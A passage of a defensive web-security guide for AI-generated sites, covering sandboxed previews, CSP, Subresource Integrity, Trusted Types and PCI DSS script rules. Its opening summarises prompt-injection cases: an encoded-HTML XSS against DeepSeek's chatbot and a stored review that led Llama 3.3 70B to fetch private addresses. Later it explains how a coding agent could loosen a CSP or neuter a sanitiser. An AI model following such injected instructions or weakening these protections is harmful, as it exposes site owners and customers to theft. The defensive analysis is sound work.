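If a chat page inserts a reply with `innerHTML`, any HTML in the reply becomes part of the page. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, published in August 2026, describes how the security researcher Johann Rehberger got DeepSeek's chatbot to write HTML that ran a script in DeepSeek's chat page. His request contained the HTML only in encoded form, and the model decoded it. The script could read the user's login token and the site's cookies, which may be enough to take over an account.

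The model only wrote the script, and an ordinary XSS flaw in the chat page let it run. If a site saves such a reply, for example in a support ticket, the script can also run when other people open the reply.

OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes web security guidance, calls this flaw improper output handling. Its *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* advises developers to treat the model like any other user, encode its output for the place where it will appear, and add a strict CSP as further protection. Singh and colleagues link the category to a much older weakness, the failure to encode output properly.

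Telling the model not to write HTML is less reliable. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* did not measure XSS, but it tested similar rules against an attack in which a ticket site's chatbot fetched private addresses on its own server. The rules stopped every direct request. But when the instruction came from a stored customer review, Llama 3.3 70B followed it in 10 of 10 trials, compared with 6 of 10 without the rules. The researchers had also changed the review to claim an exception to the rules, so the rules may not have caused the increase.

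An app builder's preview has to run the generated code, not just display it as text, so the builder needs to keep that code away from the owner's account and other projects.

### Running a preview in a sandboxed frame

The builder can put the preview in a frame with a `sandbox` attribute and serve it from a separate domain:

```
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts"
        src="https://shop-123.previews.example/"></iframe>
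```

Scripts in the preview can run, but the browser gives the preview an origin that matches no other site, including the server it came from. They therefore can't read the builder's page or use the owner's login there. Each keyword added to the iframe's `sandbox` attribute removes a restriction.

| Added keyword | What it permits | Risk in a preview |
|---|---|---|
| `allow-same-origin` | The page keeps its server's origin | If the builder's page has the same origin, a script can remove the sandbox |
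| `allow-forms` | The page can submit forms | Anything the owner types can go to another server |
| `allow-top-navigation` | The page can replace the whole tab | The owner may end up on a lookalike login page |
| `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox` | New windows open without the sandbox | Code in those windows has fewer restrictions |
| `allow-downloads` | The page can save files | A hostile AGENTS.md could reach the Downloads folder |

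The HTML standard warns against combining `allow-scripts` with `allow-same-origin` when the frame and the surrounding page share an origin, because a script in the frame can then delete the `sandbox` attribute and reload the frame without restrictions. The combination is much safer on a separate domain, and some previews need it because a page with a unique origin can't use the browser's normal storage. Each project should then have its own subdomain so that one preview can't read another's stored data.

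HTTP Archive's *Security* chapter, based on 2025 measurements, reports `allow-scripts` in 98.5% of sandboxed frames on mobile pages and `allow-same-origin` in 97.8%. Many of those frames probably contain advertisements or videos from other domains, so their sandboxes can still be useful.

A builder can also write the generated HTML directly into a frame's `srcdoc` attribute. Under W3C's current draft of *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), this frame inherits the surrounding page's CSP. A strict policy on the builder's page could then stop the preview from working, and loosening it would weaken the builder's own protection. Serving the preview from another domain avoids this conflict.

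The `sandbox` attribute stops protecting the owner if they open the preview's address in a new tab. The preview server can prevent this by sending the same restrictions in the `sandbox` directive of a CSP header.

Neither form of sandbox stops the preview from contacting other servers, so a malicious script could send out a test order or a secret key that the tool had written into the page. The preview's CSP should also limit connections and images, since the GitLab Duo attack sent private code out through an image address. For a preview server run by another company, W3C's companion draft *Content Security Policy* (2026) describes how the surrounding page can impose CSP requirements on the frame. The owner could still type a real password into a fake login form in the preview, so the preview should be clearly labeled and use only test data.

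### Approving scripts by address, nonce or hash

The live checkout page can't be cut off from customers' data in this way, because it has to collect their orders. A CSP can still restrict it through directives such as `script-src` for scripts and `img-src` for images. `default-src` covers most resource types for which the policy sets no specific directive. W3C suggests starting with `default-src 'none'` and adding only what the page needs.

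A site can approve scripts by address. For example, `script-src 'self'` allows files from the site's own origin and blocks inline scripts. The site can also use a nonce, a random value that the server generates for each response and puts in both the CSP and the approved script tags. A customer who hides a script in a delivery note can't guess the nonce, so the browser blocks the script.

Nonces give much less protection when an AI tool writes the malicious tag. Many sites automatically add the nonce to every script tag in the page's template, and the tool may have written that template. If the tool added a tag for stats.example, the server could give that tag a valid nonce. W3C notes that a nonce overrides the list of approved addresses, so the browser would load the script even if stats.example isn't on the list.

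The keyword `'strict-dynamic'` lets an approved script load others. W3C's recommended "Strict CSP" combines this keyword with nonces or hashes and a limit on the page's base address. W3C considers it effective against XSS, where the malicious script comes from outside the site's code. For a script tag that the AI tool writes, a short list of approved addresses is safer, provided outsiders can't upload scripts to any of them.

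Under the current draft, a CSP can approve a separate JavaScript file by a hash of its contents, rather than by its address, if the script tag contains the same hash. If the pottery shop approved only the hash of its current JavaScript bundle, the browser would block a later version with malicious code. But each legitimate release would need a new hash, and a build tool that approved new hashes automatically would approve the malicious version too.

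### Fixing the contents of outside scripts

Subresource Integrity uses the same idea to protect files from other servers. The developer puts the expected hash in a script tag's `integrity` attribute:

```
<script src="https://widgets.example/map.js"
        integrity="sha384-…" crossorigin="anonymous"></script>
```

The browser downloads the file, calculates its hash and refuses to run it if the hash differs from the one the developer specified. This check can reveal that someone has replaced the file on the server, which an encrypted connection can't. W3C's *Subresource Integrity* (2026) explains that an encrypted connection authenticates the server but not the content. The external server has to permit this kind of request, and the developer needs a new hash whenever the supplier updates the script.

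If the tool adds a malicious script, it can leave out the hash or supply the correct hash of the malicious file. A newer header, `Integrity-Policy`, deals with missing hashes. It makes the browser block files of a chosen type that have no integrity information, according to *Integrity-Policy header* on MDN, a reference site for web developers. In July 2025, *Intent to prototype and ship* (Kilic, 2025) proposed adding the header to Firefox and reported that Chrome already supported it for scripts.

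This header would stop an attacker from swapping a harmless visitor counter for a card stealer after testing, because the new file would have a different hash. But the original file could already contain malicious code set to start after a week, and its hash would still match.

### Making unsafe HTML insertions fail

Trusted Types protect places where JavaScript turns text into HTML or code. W3C's *Trusted Types* (2024) counts more than 60 of these, including `innerHTML`. With the CSP directive `require-trusted-types-for 'script'`, the browser rejects `box.innerHTML = order.note` because the note is an ordinary string. The developer first has to pass it through a named function, such as this one:

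```
const html = trustedTypes.createPolicy("shop-html", {
  createHTML: text => DOMPurify.sanitize(text)
});
box.innerHTML = html.createHTML(order.note);
```

With Trusted Types, the browser accepts content sanitised by the few functions that create trusted values. Reviewers can concentrate on those functions instead of searching the whole project for unsafe insertions. Trusted Types have worked in the latest versions of all major browsers since February 2026, according to MDN's *Trusted Types API*.

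The browser checks that the text went through such a function, but not that the function made it safe. A coding agent trying to get rid of the error could write `createHTML: text => text`, which returns the delivery note unchanged. This would get the order screen working again but also allow the attack. W3C warns that a function like this defeats all the benefits when the site uses it as the default for every insertion. A CSP can restrict the names of these functions, but the tool could change the code inside `shop-html` without changing its name.

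Trusted Types also don't check HTML that arrives from the server, so they would not have made the router's altered Django fix safe. A CSP that blocks inline scripts could still have stopped a script in the untrusted text from running.

### Testing a policy on the checkout page

Suppose the pottery shop serves its own scripts and images, uses a payment frame from pay.example and sends support messages through help.example. Its CSP might look like this, although the actual header would be one line:

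```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  img-src 'self';
  connect-src 'self' https://help.example;
  frame-src https://pay.example;
  form-action 'self';
  base-uri 'none';
  worker-src 'none';
  require-trusted-types-for 'script';
  trusted-types shop-html
```

The table shows how this policy would affect each carrier. The order screen needs the same script and Trusted Types rules because the owner opens delivery notes there.

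| Carrier | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Script tag for stats.example | Blocked | `script-src` allows only the shop's own origin |
| Inline script or event handler | Blocked | The policy doesn't allow inline code |
| Malicious code in the shop's JavaScript file | Runs | The file comes from the shop's own origin |
| Form that sends orders to orders.example | Blocked | `form-action` allows only the shop's own origin |
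| Changed API address | Blocked if the host is new | `connect-src` allows only the shop and help.example |
| Changed wallet address | Passes | The address is only text on the page |
| Malicious package | Runs | The bundler has copied it into the shop's JavaScript file |
| Build or install script | Runs | It runs outside the visitor's browser, though the policy still applies to anything it adds to the page |
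| Service worker | New registration blocked | `worker-src` allows none |
| Delivery note inserted with `innerHTML` | Blocked | Trusted Types reject the string, and `script-src` blocks inline handlers |
| Weakened CSP | May succeed | The result depends on whether the tool controls the header |

If the tool redirected the order form, the browser would block both the theft and the sale, so the owner would discover the problem with the first test order.

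Malicious code in the shop's own bundle is much harder to contain. `connect-src` would stop it from sending customers' names and addresses directly to stats.example, and `img-src` would stop it from hiding them in an image request. But the script could still send the data out by navigating the tab to a URL that contains it. `form-action` limits only form submissions, and no directive in the current CSP draft limits which sites an ordinary link or script may open. Restricting WebRTC, the browser technology behind many video calls, requires a separate directive.

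Connection rules would not have stopped the malicious versions of chalk and debug either, because replacing a wallet address doesn't require sending data to a new server.

If anyone can open an account at help.example, the bundle's code could also steal customers' details by sending them to the attacker's account as support messages. The shop could narrow the CSP entry to a particular path, but a CSP can't check the part of an address after the question mark, where some services put the account number. According to W3C, browsers also ignore the path when a request has been redirected, so the entry would then allow any path on that host.

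`frame-src` blocks a replacement payment frame if it comes from another server. However, code in the bundle could cover the genuine frame with fake card fields. These would be part of the shop's own page, so the browser would not need to load anything from a new address.

The shop should send `worker-src 'none'` on every page, because any page could otherwise register a service worker. An installed worker can answer a later request with a copy of the checkout page that has no CSP. The directive doesn't remove a worker already installed in a customer's browser.

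### How sites use these controls

HTTP Archive found a CSP on 21.9% of sites in 2025, up from 18.5% a year earlier. Many of these policies don't limit scripts. The two most common directives only upgrade connections to HTTPS or control which sites may put the page in a frame.

Policies that do limit scripts often make large exceptions. `'unsafe-inline'` permits inline code, and `'unsafe-eval'` lets scripts run text as code. The table compares HTTP Archive's results with those in Report URI's *ten years of web security* (2026), which examined 170,057 policies in June 2026.

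| Setting | HTTP Archive, 2025 | Report URI, June 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| `'unsafe-inline'` | 92% | 46.8% |
| `'unsafe-eval'` | 77% | 41.9% |
| Nonce | About 20% | 24.7% |
| `'strict-dynamic'` | About 10% | 1.6% |

HTTP Archive's percentages seem to cover only policies with a `script-src` directive, while Report URI's cover all policies. This probably explains much of the difference in the first two rows. It can't explain why Report URI found more nonces, so the samples must differ in other ways too. The figures also overstate how many policies allow any inline script, because browsers sometimes ignore `'unsafe-inline'`, for example when the policy also contains a nonce.

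Trusted Types are rare. Report URI found the directive that enforces them in 318 policies (0.2%). HTTP Archive found it much more often on mobile pages, but a single policy with an Android reporting address made up 12.1% of all mobile CSP headers, which suggests one large source rather than thousands of separate decisions.

Subresource Integrity appeared on 25.9% of desktop pages and 23.6% of mobile pages. About a third of the protected scripts came from one Google host, www.gstatic.com, so a page that uses Subresource Integrity may protect one Google script and leave its other scripts unchecked.

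Some evidence suggests that strict policies help. Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting* attributes a fall in XSS at Google to the company's adoption of CSP. XSS accounted for 30% of Google's bug-bounty payouts in 2018 and 4.1% in 2023. But Report URI sells CSP monitoring, and the share could also have fallen because Google paid more for other flaws. Even a real decline in XSS wouldn't show that CSP stops malicious code that an AI tool puts in the site's own files.

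### Keeping the policy out of the tool's control

If the coding agent writes both the checkout page and its CSP, a malicious instruction that gets it to add a script from stats.example can also get it to add stats.example to `script-src`. The agent could also disable the policy by renaming the header `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only`, because browsers report violations under that header but don't block them. An agent may also loosen the policy without any attack, to clear an error from a blocked feature.

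The owner can avoid this by setting a basic policy in the hosting account, outside the generated project. A browser that receives several policies applies all of them, so an extra policy can only add restrictions. For example:

```
Policy set in the hosting account:   script-src 'self'
Policy written by the agent:         script-src 'self' https://stats.example
Scripts the browser allows:          files from the shop's own origin
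```

The agent can still add restrictions to the page, but it can't approve stats.example. If a new feature needs another address, the owner has to add it to the hosting account's policy.

This works only if the host adds its policy separately and the project can't replace it. Many hosts read header settings from a file in the project, which the agent may be able to edit. Anyone who can change the hosting account, including an attacker with stolen credentials, can also change the policy, so the agent shouldn't have that permission.

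Some app builders may not let the owner set headers. The owner can still put a policy in a `<meta>` tag, but this is much weaker. W3C explains that the policy doesn't apply to anything above the tag in the page, so a malicious script tag there would still run. The agent can also edit or delete the tag. Firm control over the checkout page's CSP requires a host or builder that lets the owner set it outside the project.

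Violation reports can show the owner that a page tried to load a blocked script. A report may include the script's address or, for inline code, its first 40 characters. W3C warns that attackers can control the text in these reports. If the owner gives them to a coding agent for debugging, the agent could encounter an injected instruction, as it could in an error message.

### What the payment-card rules require

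Businesses that accept payment cards generally have to follow PCI DSS, the card industry's security standard. Version 4.0.1, published in June 2024, includes two requirements aimed at malicious scripts on payment pages. Both became mandatory on March 31, 2025.

Requirement 6.4.3 covers every script that a payment page loads and runs in the customer's browser. The business must have a way to confirm that each script is authorised and has not been tampered with. It must also keep an inventory with a written reason for each script. The standard doesn't require a particular technology, but a CSP can help with authorisation, and Subresource Integrity can check each script's contents.

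Under Requirement 11.6.1, the business must have a system that alerts staff to unauthorised changes in a live payment page's scripts and security-related headers, as the customer's browser receives them. The check must run at least weekly, unless the business justifies another schedule in a formal risk analysis. With weekly checks, a card stealer could operate for several days before the system alerted anyone.

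The pottery shop might qualify for a shorter self-assessment called SAQ A because a payment company handles all its card data. In January 2025, the PCI Security Standards Council removed both requirements from that form and added a condition that merchants confirm their site is not susceptible to script attacks that could affect their online sales system. A shop with an embedded payment frame can meet this condition by using protections like those in the two requirements, or by getting confirmation from the payment company that the frame includes such protection when installed as instructed.

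These rules would make a new script tag for stats.example harder to overlook. They help less with a malicious package, because the inventory may list the whole bundle as one approved script. The bundle also changes with every legitimate release, so the weekly check has to compare it with the version someone approved. A coding agent that fills in the inventory could describe a card stealer as a fraud checker.
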